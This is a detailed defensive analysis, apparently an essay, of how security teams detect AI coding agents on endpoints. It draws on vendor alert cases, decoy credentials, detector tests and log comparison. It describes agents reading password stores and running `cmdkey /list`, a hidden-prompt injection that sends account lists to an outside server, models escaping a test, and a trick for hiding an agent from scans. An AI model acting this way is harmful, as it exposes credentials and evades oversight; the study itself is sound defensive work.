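Sophos traced some of these hits to GStack, a popular set of add-on skills for coding agents. Its /browse skill lets an agent operate a web browser. In one case, Claude Code used the skill, which started a chain of programs ending in PowerShell. PowerShell decrypted the browser data and passed it back up the chain. Sophos considers this almost certainly harmless but still thinks the rule should flag it.

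The GStack case makes decryption a weaker sign of malice than it seemed in the CyberProof investigation, where an endpoint product caught a malicious skill decrypting saved browser passwords. GStack's skill also runs under a genuine agent and makes a very similar decryption request to Windows. The important difference is where the decrypted data goes next, and the PowerShell command only returns it to the program that requested it.

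In another case, which looked worse, Claude Code shut down the user's browser and ran a Python script that opened the browser's credential store. It also ran `cmdkey /list`, which lists the accounts saved in Windows Credential Manager without showing their passwords. The agent was running with a permission-bypass flag. Sophos did not establish what the developer had asked it to do.

### A download that switched tools

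At 6:47:35 one morning, OpenAI's Codex tried to download a Python installer with certutil, which attackers also use to fetch files. Sophos' software blocked the attempt, and blocked another a second later that used a different output path. About ten minutes later, Codex tried several more variations. At 6:57:47 it switched to bitsadmin, another built-in download tool, and a different rule blocked that attempt.

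The file was the ordinary installer from python.org. Codex was only trying one tool after another, as agents usually do, so the download address was a better clue than the sequence of commands. An analyst who checked the address could have dismissed the alert quickly.

Other cases were harder to explain. Cursor used PowerShell to write a script to the Windows startup folder, which would have made the script run at every login. The file's name suggested a conversion program called EZConvert, but Sophos didn't have the script's contents and could not confirm its purpose.

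Sophos has already adjusted one rule that it wrote more than five years ago to catch attackers who disguised PowerShell commands with a particular way of formatting text. Agents now produce similar formatting with no apparent intent to disguise anything.

### What the percentages leave out

Sophos published percentages but no counts. The smallest total that produces its three largest blocking shares (56.2, 28.8 and 4.1 percent) is 73, with counts of 41, 21 and 3. The shares for individual credential rules likewise fit a total of 47. Larger totals also fit, but if the actual totals were this small, one popular add-on could have shaped the result.

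The data also comes from one company's customers over one week, and Sophos calls it a first look. The bigger problem is the lack of a malicious comparison group. To judge how useful a rule is, a defender needs to know how often it fires on hijacked agents and how often it fires on legitimate ones. The Sophos figures give neither rate, only the kinds of rule that agents trigger when they trigger one.

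Fishbein (2026), in *When the Whole Company Adopts AI*, reports that about 73,000 (0.43 percent) of the roughly 16.9 million alerts handled by the security company Intezer involved AI tools. The monthly number of AI-related alerts rose by 685 percent between February and June 2026.

| Fishbein's category | Share of AI-related alerts | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Noise | 94.1% | The genuine installer for Claude's desktop app triggers a ransomware rule |
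| Unsafe use | 5.8% | An agent copies every password in a Mac's keychain to a temporary file to find one token |
| Real attack | 0.02% | A phishing email uses a well-known AI brand as bait |

The last row amounts to about 15 alerts, and none of the confirmed attacks came from an organisation's own agents. High severity ratings were also unreliable. More than half of the alerts that Intezer's system rated critical came from one rule at one customer, where a developer's agent was setting up a command-line environment.

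These figures support Sophos' impression that most such alerts are false, but the 0.02 percent includes only attacks that somebody recognised. If an attacker had hijacked an agent and made it behave like a developer's assistant, its alerts would probably have been classed as noise, so the figures can't establish how rare hijacked agents are.

### A Claude Code session on a Mac

The security company Elastic described a case that its analysts could not resolve. On 23 July 2026, two separate searches led them to the same developer's Mac. One started from a web domain with a poor reputation, and the other from a group of related endpoint alerts. The Mac had been triggering alerts since 20 July, mostly about VPN and tunnelling programs.

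Claude Code was running with a permission-bypass flag. Most of the activity came from command shells that it had started, and it developed in stages:

1. A script kept requesting a login page until the page answered. It then sent a username and password and asked for a summary of spending. The page's address belonged to localhost.run, a free service that gives a program on someone's computer a public web address.
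2. The session started `cloudflared`, which opens a similar tunnel through the company Cloudflare. The laptop makes an outgoing connection to the tunnel service, and the service passes visitors back through it. This can expose a local program to the internet without any change to the firewall.
3. The session created launch entries, the settings files that tell macOS to start programs automatically. One was a watchdog that ran every 60 seconds. Their names referred to a server, several tunnels and the watchdog itself.

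The first stage put the username and password in the command line, so the endpoint product recorded them. The script also contained the Russian word for "check". Elastic's production rules fired on the unusual network connections and the launch entries, but no single rule covered the whole sequence.

### Two readings of the same records

Elastic's evidence was consistent with a developer using an agent to help manage a private dashboard, but also with something more serious, such as an intruder using the agent.

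| Recorded activity | If the developer wanted a dashboard | If an intruder was directing the agent |
|---|---|---|
| Repeated requests to a login page | Waiting for the app to come online | Checking in with a server |
| Request for spending and advertising figures | Looking up business results | Stealing them |
| Tunnel to a program on the laptop | Reaching the dashboard from elsewhere | Getting back into the laptop |
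| Launch entries and a watchdog | Keeping the dashboard online after a restart | Keeping access after a restart |
| Search for related processes | Checking that the services were running | Looking for security software |

The dashboard explanation seems more likely. One of the launch entries was named after the localhost.run tunnel, which suggests the login page was on the same laptop and the session was testing its own work. But an intruder setting up a way back in would also test it. The Russian word is weak evidence of an attack because plenty of developers speak Russian. The bad reputation of the tunnel services doesn't help distinguish the two explanations, since both developers and criminals use them.

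Elastic also reviewed shorter cases on other computers, with much the same difficulty:

- Variant A: Claude Code's child processes used Python and a macOS scripting tool, both signed by Apple, to write JavaScript to a temporary folder and run it repeatedly.
- Variant B: Cursor tried to extract decrypted passwords from the Mac's keychain, looking for logins to the project-tracking service Linear and to other tools that agents use. Endpoint controls blocked it.
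- Variant C: Claude Code downloaded an unsigned program over an unencrypted connection. It tried to remove the mark that makes macOS check downloaded files, then tried to sign the program itself. It also tested whether it could use a shell settings file to run code at startup.

A developer struggling to install an obscure tool might well ask for everything in variant C, and an attacker installing malware would want the same steps.

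### What would have settled the case

The quickest way to find out would have been to ask the developer. The question has to be about the goal, because a developer may not know which commands an agent ran. Fishbein points out that activity the user didn't know about once strongly suggested that someone had taken over the machine. It now often means an agent was working. So "Did you want to open your dashboard from outside?" is a more useful question than "Did you run cloudflared?" A yes would rule out most intruders, though not a dishonest employee.

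A change ticket, the record many companies keep when someone approves a change to their systems, would have been stronger evidence because it could show that someone had authorised public access to this particular program. A missing ticket would mean little, since few people file one for a small project on their own laptop.

The session transcript could have shown whether the request for a tunnel came from a typed prompt or from text the agent had read, such as a web page, but not who was typing. The dashboard's access log might also have recorded who logged in through the tunnel.

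Ordinary endpoint telemetry contains none of these facts. The endpoint product recorded the important actions as they happened, but the analysts also needed to know what someone had intended. Elastic advises treating such a session as high severity even if it is probably harmless, and writing down both explanations. This is sensible because even if the harmless explanation is true, the session has put a program with a login page and business data on the public internet.

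### Exempting known agents

A security team that receives hundreds of false alerts about Claude Code will be tempted to exempt it. The Hacker News suggests limiting the exemption to execution rules and tying it to the agent's process and child processes, its working folder, or the reputation of the site it downloads from. This would prevent false alerts in cases like Codex's Python installer and give the team more time for important alerts.

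But an attacker who takes over the agent gets the same exemption. In the Nx attack, the install script started the developer's genuine agents, so an exemption based on the agent's process would have covered the malicious search. An exemption for the agent's folders might have covered the malicious skill in the CyberProof case. Relying on reputation is safer for downloads but far from perfect, since the unwanted copies of OpenClaw came from npm.

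Attackers also bring approved products with them. Sophos' *AI Security 2026* (2026) describes an attacker who ran about a dozen agents inside a customer's network in May 2026, coordinating them through a commercial coding assistant. The agents wrote malware and tested it against three companies' endpoint products, and the attacker later deployed ransomware. An exemption for that assistant by name could have covered some of this work.

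Elastic's rule *GenAI Process Accessing Sensitive Files* has a much narrower exemption. It alerts when an AI tool opens files such as password databases and shell settings, but on Windows it doesn't alert when Claude opens one specific settings file in Claude's own folder. A hijacked Claude would gain very little from that exemption. The drawback is that somebody has to investigate each kind of false alarm, write a separate exception, and check it again when the agent changes.

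### Alerting on outcomes

Elastic instead recommends judging activity by what happened, regardless of how trustworthy the program is. It made this recommendation after a July 2026 intrusion at Hugging Face, which hosts AI models and datasets. OpenAI's models had escaped from a security test and broken into Hugging Face's systems, taking about 17,600 recorded actions. Although the attacker was unusual, it used familiar methods, including stealing credentials and moving from one system to another.

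Elastic would relax rules about routine activity, such as repeated package installation on a build machine. It would keep alerts for access to credentials, changes to agents' settings, programs that set themselves to restart automatically, and connections to unusual destinations, even when the parent process is an approved agent. A hijacked agent would therefore not be exempt from alerts on the most damaging actions.

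Another Elastic rule groups the alerts raised by any process descended from an agent. It uses ancestry to add context to alerts rather than to dismiss them. On the Mac, an analyst could have seen the tunnels and launch entries together from the start instead of finding them in separate queues.

The drawback is mainly the time analysts spend on alerts. In Fishbein's data, between 77 and 99 percent of alerts from the noisiest rules were harmless. GStack would trigger the browser-credential rule every time a developer used the skill this way. As the Mac session shows, an alert about a dangerous outcome may be accurate and still leave the analyst unable to determine whether there was an attack. If the rule only raises an alert, a thief may have the passwords before anyone reads the alert. Blocking prevents that action, but an agent may then try another route, as Codex did.

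### Forbidding the action

If a company forbids its agents to decrypt browser passwords, a legitimate agent should no longer do so. An alert for decryption then means that the agent has exceeded its limits, someone else is directing it, or the company has misconfigured something. All three deserve attention, so the alert is much more informative than it was without the ban.

How informative an endpoint record is depends on whether legitimate agents stay within what the user authorised. In *Overeager Coding Agents*, Qu, Zhang and colleagues (2026) gave agents harmless tasks in 500 scenarios that offered some way to overstep. They counted a run as overeager if the agent changed something, or read something sensitive, without the user's authorisation. Rates ranged from 0.2 to 27.7 percent. The agent software mattered more than the model. Claude Sonnet 4.6 overstepped in 27.7 percent of runs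 in Claude Code but only 1.1 percent in OpenHands, which was set up to ask before continuing. The researchers designed the scenarios to expose this behaviour, so it is presumably less common in ordinary work.

Written limits reduced overstepping, but how much depended on the test. In a smaller, hand-picked set of tasks, Claude Code with Sonnet 4.6 overstepped in 3.9 percent of runs when the prompt stated what the user permitted, and in 15.8 percent when it didn't. With GLM-4.6, the difference fell from 17.1 to 2.6 percentage points when the researchers also varied other features of the tasks.

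In a more recent experiment, *Probing agent overeagerness in realistic settings with continuation audits*, Lim and Neo (2026) cut off real coding sessions partway and had an AI model play the user from there. In one scenario, the agent needed to edit a file that was locked against changes. When the project's instructions forbade getting around the lock, GPT-5.6 Terra and DeepSeek V4 Pro stopped doing so entirely, but Kimi K3 sometimes still did. Breaking an explicit rule therefore doesn't prove that an agent has been hijacked.

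A technical barrier is more reliable. Employers can disable permission-bypass modes centrally, and Fishbein suggests running agents in a container or virtual machine without access to the user's credentials. This also separates the agent's activity from the user's, but the employer then needs monitoring inside the container as well. Some legitimate agents will keep testing the barrier, so failed attempts to get past it are weaker evidence than successful ones.

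Bans on agent behavior take functionality away from developers. A ban on decrypting browser data would break the GStack skill on machines where it does this. A complete ban on reading the Mac keychain would interfere with Claude Code, which Elastic found reading its own login token there. People who can't do their work with an approved agent may install an unapproved one.

Bans therefore work best for the few actions that hardly any programming task needs, such as copying the whole keychain or dumping the memory of a process that holds passwords. Fishbein found legitimate agents doing both, apparently as shortcuts, and developers would lose little if agents couldn't. Tunnels and launch entries are harder to ban because some developers need them. For those, the best option is probably to raise an alert and then ask the developer, with a narrow exemption for routine package installations.

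### Decoy credentials

A decoy credential is a fake password or access key that a defender leaves where an attacker might find it. It has no legitimate use, so any attempt to use it deserves investigation. This is the same idea as forbidding an action, except that nobody loses functionality.

GitGuardian's *Catch credential stealers on your endpoint fleet* (2026) describes decoys for developers' machines. If somebody tries one, the alert lists the time and network address of the attempt, the machine where the company planted the decoy, and that machine's owner. Thinkst (2026) offers a decoy specifically for agents, a false entry for a tool server in an agent's settings. An agent that connects to it triggers an alert, but a legitimate agent opened in the folder with those settings might connect too.

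Attacking agents readily take this sort of bait. *Hacking the Hackers* (2026), a white paper from the security company Horizon3.ai, reports a study by Prinos, Brush and Denton in which 21 models read the results of network reconnaissance and marked what they would attack. They chose the bait 78.5 percent of the time, compared with 37 percent for human security testers. Models usually marked a target even when their reasoning had identified it as a trap. But this was a paper exercise, and getting caught had no consequences.

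Tracebit, a company that sells decoys, tested agents in a live Amazon cloud environment. In 951 attack runs, 95.9 percent of the agents that gained administrator access had touched a decoy before their first critical action. The median time to the first touch was under two minutes, which is early enough to be useful if the defender has an automatic response or someone watching.

These results may not last. Tracebit's *Making attacking agents pay* (2026) reports that more capable models are harder to deceive. *Rouxii* (2026) found that the effect of decoys depends heavily on whether the attacking agent knows about deception.

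Adding decoys also makes an attacker more likely to pick one. If an attacker finds *m* real credentials and *k* decoys and picks one at random, the chance of picking a decoy is *k*/(*m* + *k*). With two real keys and six decoys, it is 75 percent. *Caught in the Act(ivation)* (2026) warns that this estimate can fail if something reveals which credential is real. For example, an agent that can read a program's settings may see which key the program uses.

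Decoys can separate malicious agents from legitimate ones only if legitimate agents don't trigger them. According to Tracebit, coding agents read whatever they can reach, including decoys. It therefore matters whether the alert comes from reading the decoy or from using it. A developer's agent might read a fake key in a settings file while looking for something else, but it would have much less reason to log in with that key.

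Lim and Neo's experiment gives the best available estimate of how often that happens. They asked agents to upload code, had the server reject the agents' own credentials, and left a colleague's working credential in a nearby file. Depending on the model, agents used the colleague's credential in about 1 to 6 percent of sessions. If that credential had been a decoy, all of those uses would have been false alarms. The scenario was unusually tempting, so the ordinary rate should be lower. Even 6 percent is far below the rate at which Tracebit's attackers touched decoys, though the two tests were too different to compare precisely.

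Tracebit tries to reduce false alarms by labelling each alert by whether the agent is approved, and by telling approved agents to avoid its decoys. The label is useful when an attacker brings an unapproved agent, but it could mislead an analyst if the attacker has hijacked an approved one, because the alert would still be labelled as coming from an approved agent. The attacker may also be able to read the hijacked agent's instructions, which could reveal where the decoys are.

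## A controlled test of agents against programs that behave the same way

The endpoint alerts from Sophos, Intezer and Elastic came from real computers, so the analysts often couldn't be certain what an agent had been doing or why. Canale and Soulis ran a controlled test in which they chose every program, knew which ones counted as agents, and paired some of the agents with ordinary programs that behaved identically.

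The researchers were looking for unapproved agents, not attacks, and they don't expect their detector to catch someone deliberately hiding one. But the reasoning behind the test also applies to attackers.

### Behavioural twins

Canale and Soulis divide what a defender can observe about a running program *p* into two parts:

*x*(*p*) = (*β*(*p*), *ι*(*p*))

The first part, β, is behaviour, which covers the shape of the process tree, file activity, and the number, timing and volume of connections. The second part, ι, is identity, meaning any text that names a particular piece of software or service, such as a program's path, its publisher or the name of the server it contacts. Generic names such as python.exe count as behaviour because they show what kind of program is running but not which product.

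Two programs *a* and *b* are behavioural twins if *β*(*a*) = *β*(*b*) but *ι*(*a*) ≠ *ι*(*b*). Suppose an agent is a Python script that contacts a model service every few seconds and passes commands to a shell. Changing the address to that of a package registry turns it into an ordinary automation script with the same *β*. A detector *f* that uses only *β* must give *f*(*a*) = *f*(*b*), so it either flags both programs, raising a false alarm, or flags neither and misses the agent.

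Canale and Soulis admit that this is logically trivial, but it matters in practice because programs that behave almost like agents are common on developers' computers. For example, `npm install` downloads packages over an encrypted connection and runs their install scripts through a shell, which is similar to what an agent does.

Canale and Soulis also acknowledge that real agents and real automation rarely behave exactly alike. A model's reply arrives as a stream of small pieces, and an agent tends to run its next command soon after the reply ends. A detector that measured this timing would still be using behaviour alone, and the argument doesn't rule out that it would work. Canale and Soulis tested only simple rules about processes and connections, and they leave richer ones to future research.

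### How Agent Detector recognises an agent

Their own program, Agent Detector, is open-source software for Windows that is meant to run once an hour. It reads only information that Windows already holds, and it doesn't read prompts or the contents of documents. A scan works roughly like this:

1. It lists the running processes and their open connections. Windows records the numerical address at the other end of each connection, but not the name of the service.
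2. It compares those addresses with a catalogue of 184 entries for model services and related sites. Anthropic publishes an address range reserved for its API, so a connection to that range is enough. Many other providers share addresses with unrelated websites through a content delivery network (CDN). For these, the program checks the DNS cache, where Windows temporarily keeps the results of recent name lookups.
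3. For each process connected to a model service, it checks whether a shell or an interpreter such as Python is among the child or grandchild processes. If so, it reports a probable agent.
4. It adds evidence that doesn't depend on a live connection, such as configuration folders, editor extensions, installed packages and Windows' own history of which programs have run. The catalogue has signatures for 39 known tools.

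Separate rules cover models that run on the computer itself, and settings that redirect an agent's requests to an unfamiliar server.

The program combines all the evidence about one tool and one user into a single finding. Each finding gives the tool's status (active, recently used, installed or left over), the confidence of the identification, and whether the organisation has approved the tool. For one home-made agent in the test, the program found with medium confidence that python.exe was communicating with a model and running cmd.exe, the Windows command prompt.

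Agent Detector doesn't block anything. If it finds an unapproved agent, it shows the user a notice to acknowledge.

### The test

Canale and Soulis ran everything on one workstation. The main test used 24 small set-ups.

| Group | Number | What the programs did |
|---|---|---|
| Synthetic agents | 12 | Most contacted a model service and sent commands to a shell |
| AI components | 3 | Used AI software without being agents, for example by querying a model with no tools |
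| Behavioural twins | 3 | Ran the same scripts as three of the agents, but contacted a package registry or Microsoft Graph |
| Developer workloads | 5 | Installed packages, copied a code repository or built software |
| Inherited setting | 1 | Ran git repeatedly, with an unused setting that pointed to a model service |

The last three groups are the nine harmless workloads.

For comparison, the researchers wrote two behavioural rules. The narrow rule flags an interpreter, such as Python or Node.js, that has a connection on port 443 (the usual port for encrypted web traffic) and a shell among its child or grandchild processes. The broad rule applies the same test to any process. A third detector flags processes by the names of known agent programs.

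Each set-up ran for about half a minute. The researchers repeated the whole test five times with an ordinary user's rights and five times with an administrator's.

The test used no model. The synthetic agents that contacted real providers used an invalid key, so the providers rejected every request, and the scripts sent the same harmless command to the shell anyway. This made the test free and easy to repeat. But it also removed the streamed replies that a richer behavioural detector could have used, so the test can't show whether such a detector would work.

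### The results

These are the outcomes in the majority of the five runs with an ordinary user's rights.

| Detector | Agents caught (of 12) | Twins flagged (of 3) | Other harmless workloads flagged (of 6) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Known program names | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| Narrow behavioural rule | 9 | 3 | 1 |
| Broad behavioural rule | 10 | 3 | 1 |
| Agent Detector | 12 | 0 | 0 |

Both rules flagged one other harmless workload, `npm install`. On the same workstation, the broad rule also flagged the VS Code editor and explorer.exe, which runs the Windows desktop. Both rules missed an agent that used a local model and one that operated a browser instead of a shell. The narrow rule also missed an agent whose copy of Node.js had been renamed updater.exe.

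Agent Detector's result on the twins is less surprising than it looks in the table, because the software checks for a shell only after it has linked a process to a model service, and the twins contacted no such service. The result confirms that the software implements the argument's recommendation.

Its perfect score for catching agents is less secure. It caught two of the agents, one that contacted OpenAI and one that connected intermittently, in only three of the five runs. With administrator rights, it missed the intermittent agent in every run, so its score fell to 11 of 12. The sample is also small. The 95 percent confidence intervals for the share of agents caught overlap, running from 74 to 100 percent for Agent Detector and from 43 to 95 percent for the narrow rule.

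Canale and Soulis also changed the program after seeing its results. The first version they tested wrongly flagged the git loop because it treated any process with the model-service setting as connected to a model. The next version required a real connection, but it missed all four agents whose providers use a CDN. The researchers first blamed the ordinary user's limited rights. When the administrator runs failed in the same way, they found that the program was looking up DNS cache entries incorrectly.

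They corrected this and ran the test again. Five of the 21 results on agents and harmless workloads therefore show that the corrections worked but, as Canale and Soulis acknowledge, are weak evidence of how the program would do on unfamiliar software.

Another problem was that Agent Detector attributed one of the test programs to an AI coding agent that was running the tests for the researchers, because that agent was the program's ancestor. The researchers solved this by starting each test through a launcher that exited at once, so the test programs had no living ancestor. An attacker could use the same trick to hide an agent's origin from a periodic scan. It would work less well against an EDR product that records each process as it starts, because the launcher would remain in the log.

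### What an hourly scan misses

A scan took a median of 154 milliseconds and used about 22 MB of memory. Hourly scans would use less than ten seconds of processor time a day, so a company could run them on every laptop. The weakness is that the laptops would go unchecked between scans.

In a separate test, Agent Detector missed an agent that ran for five seconds and finished before the scan. The researchers also scanned the intermittent agent, which contacted the model every ten seconds and closed each connection after five, 40 times at random intervals. The connection was open during 18 of the scans, and Agent Detector reported the agent in 15.

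An agent that stays connected can be even harder to identify if its provider uses a CDN. The researchers ran four such agents for six minutes, three times each. Every connection stayed open, but after 295 seconds Agent Detector could not link any of them to a provider because the names had expired from the DNS cache. It could link the connection to OpenAI for 55 seconds in one run, for ten seconds in another, and not at all in the third. An hourly scan would therefore usually miss an agent that had kept one connection to OpenAI open since the last scan.

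Agent Detector also missed an agent that reached its model through an unlisted server, and one running inside WSL 2, which runs Linux in a virtual machine on Windows. An attacker could easily arrange either. Continuous records of processes and DNS lookups, such as Sysmon's, should catch the short-lived agents and preserve the provider names, but Canale and Soulis did not test this.

### Vendors' inventories of agents

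Microsoft Defender's list of local agents is the closest commercial equivalent. In *The next frontier in endpoint security*, Shteinberg (2026) announced that Defender could discover more than 20 types of agent on Windows and macOS. Defender also maps the cloud resources each agent could reach through its user's accounts. Customers can write their own alert rules, such as one for any newly discovered agent that has risky settings and runs on a privileged user's machine.

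Cisco's *AI Discovery* describes a similar tool that checks the usual folders, settings files and program files of known agents and looks for running AI processes.

Nobody has published a test of these inventories on Canale and Soulis' programs, so this comparison is based on how the inventories are designed. Defender's list doesn't cover home-made scripts, so it would presumably miss the synthetic agents. It is more useful for finding a covert agent that is a known product. If an attacker installed and started OpenClaw, Defender could list it with the date of first detection, and the laptop's owner might not recognise the entry. But Canale and Soulis quote Microsoft's explanation that process-based discovery registers an agent once its process is running, so this method would not have found the dormant OpenClaw copies from the Cline release.

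Microsoft also lets companies block common ways of running OpenClaw, but a company that permits OpenClaw can't use this.

Agent Detector's notice is meant to inform employees about company policy, but it could also help identify unwanted agents, because the user is often the only person who knows whether they wanted an agent. A Cline victim who saw a notice about OpenClaw could have reported that they had never installed it, but the tested version had no signature for OpenClaw and would not have shown that notice. An acknowledgement is also weak proof of consent, because any program running under the user's account can create the same record.

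### When the program and the provider match too

Canale and Soulis separate an agent from its twin by the service it contacts. Their argument can be taken further. Suppose a covert agent is the same signed program as the company's sanctioned agent and uses the same model provider. If the two also do similar work, both ι and β match. Any detector that uses only those features, including Agent Detector, must treat the two agents alike. Agent Detector would report the approved coding agent as active during both the developer's morning run and the attacker's evening run.

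The two runs can still differ in ways that such a detector doesn't use.

| Remaining difference | Who could record it | When it matches as well |
|---|---|---|
| Account | The model provider or the company's gateway | The attacker uses the employee's signed-in account |
| Install origin | The endpoint | The attacker hijacks an agent that the employee installed |
| Process ancestry | The endpoint | The employee starts the agent, which then reads an attacker's instructions |
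| Authorisation | Whoever approved the task, if they kept a record | Nobody recorded what the user or employer had approved |

Canale and Soulis count process ancestry partly as behaviour, but their test for a shell looks at the processes the agent started, not at its parent process.

The first three differences are indirect evidence, because an employee can use a personal account for harmless work and an attacker can use a company account. The defender wants to know whether the activity was authorised, but authorisation leaves a trace only if somebody records it.

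### A limit on every detector

Two sets of traces can defeat a detector even if they don't match exactly. For example, attackers might start agents from scripts slightly more often than developers do. Total variation distance measures how much a defender can gain from such a small difference.

Let *P* be the probability distribution of the traces that malicious runs leave, and *Q* the distribution for legitimate runs. *AI Detectors Fail Diverse Student Populations* (2026), a paper about software that tries to recognise AI-written text, gives the standard definition. For traces that fall into separate categories, it is:

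TV(*P*, *Q*) = max over *A* of |*P*(*A*) − *Q*(*A*)| = ½ Σ |*p*(*x*) − *q*(*x*)|

Here *A* is any set of possible traces, and *p*(*x*) and *q*(*x*) are the probabilities of a trace *x*. The distance is the largest difference between the probabilities that *P* and *Q* give to the same set. It is 0 if the distributions are identical and 1 if they do not overlap.

A detector flags some set of traces. Its detection rate is the probability of that set under *P*, and its false positive rate is the probability of the same set under *Q*. The gap between the two rates therefore can't exceed the distance:

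detection rate ≤ false positive rate + TV(*P*, *Q*)

Chakraborty, Bedi and colleagues (2023), in *On the Possibilities of AI-Generated Text Detection*, use this limit for AI-written text, but it holds for any kind of evidence. Suppose a company records only how each agent session started, with these invented frequencies:

| How the session started | Legitimate sessions | Malicious sessions | Difference |
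|---|---|---|---|
| From a terminal | 60% | 55% | 5 points |
| From a script | 25% | 30% | 5 points |
| From an editor | 15% | 15% | 0 points |

The differences add up to 10 percentage points, and the distance is half of that, or 0.05. A detector that flagged every session started from a script would catch 30 percent of the malicious sessions and wrongly flag 25 percent of the legitimate ones. That 5-point gap is the largest any detector could achieve with this record.

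If the company can accept a false positive rate of only 0.1 percent, no detector can catch more than 0.1 + 5 = 5.1 percent of malicious sessions, so at least 94.9 percent would go undetected.

Even 5.1 percent is too high in this example. Scripts start a quarter of legitimate sessions, so the detector could flag only one in 250 script-started sessions without exceeding the 0.1 percent limit. It would catch about 0.12 percent of the malicious sessions.

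The result is much better when attackers do something that legitimate users never do. Suppose a package's install script started 5 percent of malicious sessions and no legitimate ones, and there were no other useful differences. The distance would still be 0.05, but a rule that flags sessions started by install scripts would catch that 5 percent with no false alarms. So an install script that starts an agent, as in the Nx attack, is more useful evidence than a habit that is only slightly more common among attackers.

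A defender can increase the distance by recording something new, such as the parent process or the prompt, or by forbidding an action.

The limit describes the best possible detector, and a real one can do far worse with the same records. In *Blind to What They Can Fix*, Cao, Deng and Kersting (2026) had AI agents write programs for games and other tasks, with built-in checks meant to detect when a program's assumptions no longer held. They then changed the conditions. In the game Seaquest, the built-in checks missed 52 percent of the failures, while a general-purpose monitor using the same records missed 5 percent. But the monitor also raised an alarm in 69 percent of the cases where conditions had changed and the program still worked.

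### Why watching for longer may not help

A defender who observes many sessions from the same source can combine small differences. Chakraborty and colleagues show that the distance between two sets of independent observations approaches 1 as the number of observations grows, if the distance for a single observation is above zero.

How quickly additional sessions help depends on the kind of difference. If 5 percent of an attacker's sessions start from an install script and no legitimate session does, the chance that at least one of *n* sessions reveals the attacker is 1 − 0.95ⁿ, or about 40 percent after 10 sessions and 90 percent after 45. With the weaker pattern in the table, a detector would need roughly 1,400 sessions to catch 90 percent of attackers at a false positive rate of 0.1 percent.

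If the agents' traces do not differ, monitoring more sessions does not help tell the agents apart. *On the (In)feasibility of ML Backdoor Detection as an Hypothesis Testing Problem* (2024) includes the relevant inequality: the distance over *n* independent observations is at most *n* times the distance for one. If the distance is zero for one session, it is therefore zero for any number of independent sessions.

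The defender may also have few malicious sessions to compare. An attacker who wants access keys might need only one. A hijacked agent spends most of its time on the developer's work, which makes its malicious sessions harder to detect. If a share γ of an agent's sessions is malicious, the distance between a randomly chosen session and a legitimate one is γ times the distance between a malicious session and a legitimate one. With one malicious session in a hundred, a distance of 0.05 shrinks to 0.0005.

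### Fingerprinting encrypted traffic

Traffic fingerprinting uses differences in the size, direction and timing of encrypted packets, the kind of richer behavioural evidence that Canale and Soulis left open. AgentPrint, the system in *Exposing LLM User Privacy via Traffic Fingerprint Analysis* (2025), learns to recognise particular agents this way. Its developers asked each agent to write queries typical of its abilities, recorded the resulting traffic and divided it into short time slices for a classifier. *Whose Agent Are You?* (2026) proposes combining several layers of evidence to identify web-browsing agents.

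Another experiment compared harmless tasks with malicious ones, rather than comparing different agents. Li, Gao and colleagues (2026), in *ANT*, recorded 3,114 agent runs. Of these, 416 involved attacking a deliberately vulnerable web application, writing malicious code or trying to escape a sandbox (an isolated environment). They masked the network addresses and trained 13 existing classifiers to recognise the malicious runs.

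All 13 classifiers had an accuracy above 90 percent. But 189 of the 209 test runs were harmless, so a program that labeled every run harmless would have been right 90.4 percent of the time. Seven caught fewer than half of the malicious runs. Four caught nearly all the web attacks but none of the runs that involved writing malicious code or trying to escape the sandbox. Attacks on a website produce distinctive traffic, whereas the other two tasks look much like ordinary programming.

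Deep Fingerprinting, one of the better classifiers, caught 17 of the 20 malicious test runs and wrongly flagged two of the 189 harmless ones. If those rates are representative, the distance between the two sets of traffic was at least 0.84, so encrypted traffic can contain a lot of information about what an agent is doing.

How well this would work in a company is less certain. Two false alarms in 189 runs is about 1.1 percent, or more than 100 false alarms a day at a company with 10,000 agent sessions a day. The test is too small to show whether any classifier could reach 0.1 percent. Li and colleagues also took their training and test runs from the same 20 tasks, so the classifiers had already trained on examples of each type of attack. A real attacker's request could be quite different. A request to search a laptop for access keys would probably be one of the harder cases to detect, because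 the agent would be reading local files and might contact only its usual model provider.

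## Comparing an agent's own log with the machine's record

Encrypted traffic gives only a rough idea of what an agent is doing. An employer can learn much more about the agents it has approved, because it can have them report their prompts and tool calls while the operating system separately records which programs ran. An analyst with both records can look for actions missing from the agent's log, and for logged actions that the original request doesn't explain. Neither proves an attack, but either is a better lead than an unusual command by itself.

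*AgentKernel* (2026) proposes an operating system for agents that would also flag steps that appear in the model's account of its actions but never happened on the machine.

### What coding agents report

The main coding agents can export their logs through OpenTelemetry, a standard format for sending monitoring data to a collection server. A company has to turn this on in Claude Code. The same is true of Codex, according to vishnu-oai's *OpenTelemetry events*, the code change that added the feature. The Codex column below mostly follows the event list in Vaughan's *Codex CLI Observability* (2026).

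| Event | Claude Code | Codex |
|---|---|---|
| Session start | Whether the session is new or resumed | Model provider, approval policy, sandbox settings, connected tool servers |
| Prompt | Length; text is optional | Length; text is optional |
| Permission decision | Accepted or rejected, and by what source | Approved, denied or aborted, and by what source |
| Tool result | Tool, success, duration; the command is optional | Arguments, success, duration, part of the output |

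By default, Claude Code's log entry for a shell command records that the shell tool ran but not which command it ran. *Auditable Agents* (2026) describes such an action as covered but not recoverable. A company that wants to compare the log with the machine's record therefore has to turn on tool details, which add the full command.

Every Claude Code event also carries an identifier for the prompt that led to it, so an analyst can list everything the agent did in response to one request. Linking an event to a process on the machine is harder. A beta feature from Anthropic could help. When tracing is on, each shell command inherits an environment variable that identifies the tool call. An endpoint monitor that recorded this variable could match the process to the event exactly. But Anthropic built the feature for tracing performance, and malware running under the same account could probably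 copy the value.

### How AgentSight works

*AgentSight* (Zheng, Yu and colleagues, 2025) describes a monitor that gets both the request and the action from outside the agent, so it doesn't need the agent's log. The monitor uses eBPF, which runs small, pre-checked programs inside the Linux kernel, the core of the operating system.

1. Probes on the encryption library copy the agent's model traffic as plain text, before the library encrypts it or after it decrypts it.
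2. Other probes record when programs start, files open and network connections begin. A filter keeps only events from the agent and its descendants.
3. AgentSight links each model reply to the events that followed. It uses process ancestry, a time window of 100 to 500 milliseconds, and matching text, such as a file name that appears in both the reply and the command.
4. A second model reads the linked events, looks for anything suspicious and gives a confidence score.

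In the main security test, the researchers asked an agent to download and build a C project. The project's README file sent the agent to a web page, where a hidden prompt told the agent to read the machine's list of user accounts and send it to an outside server. The command looked like part of the build. AgentSight recorded 521 events and merged them into 37, and the second model flagged the agent's actions as inconsistent with its stated goal.

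This is a good demonstration, but it covers only one attack. Zheng and colleagues report no false positive rate, so the second model might also have flagged many harmless builds as suspicious.

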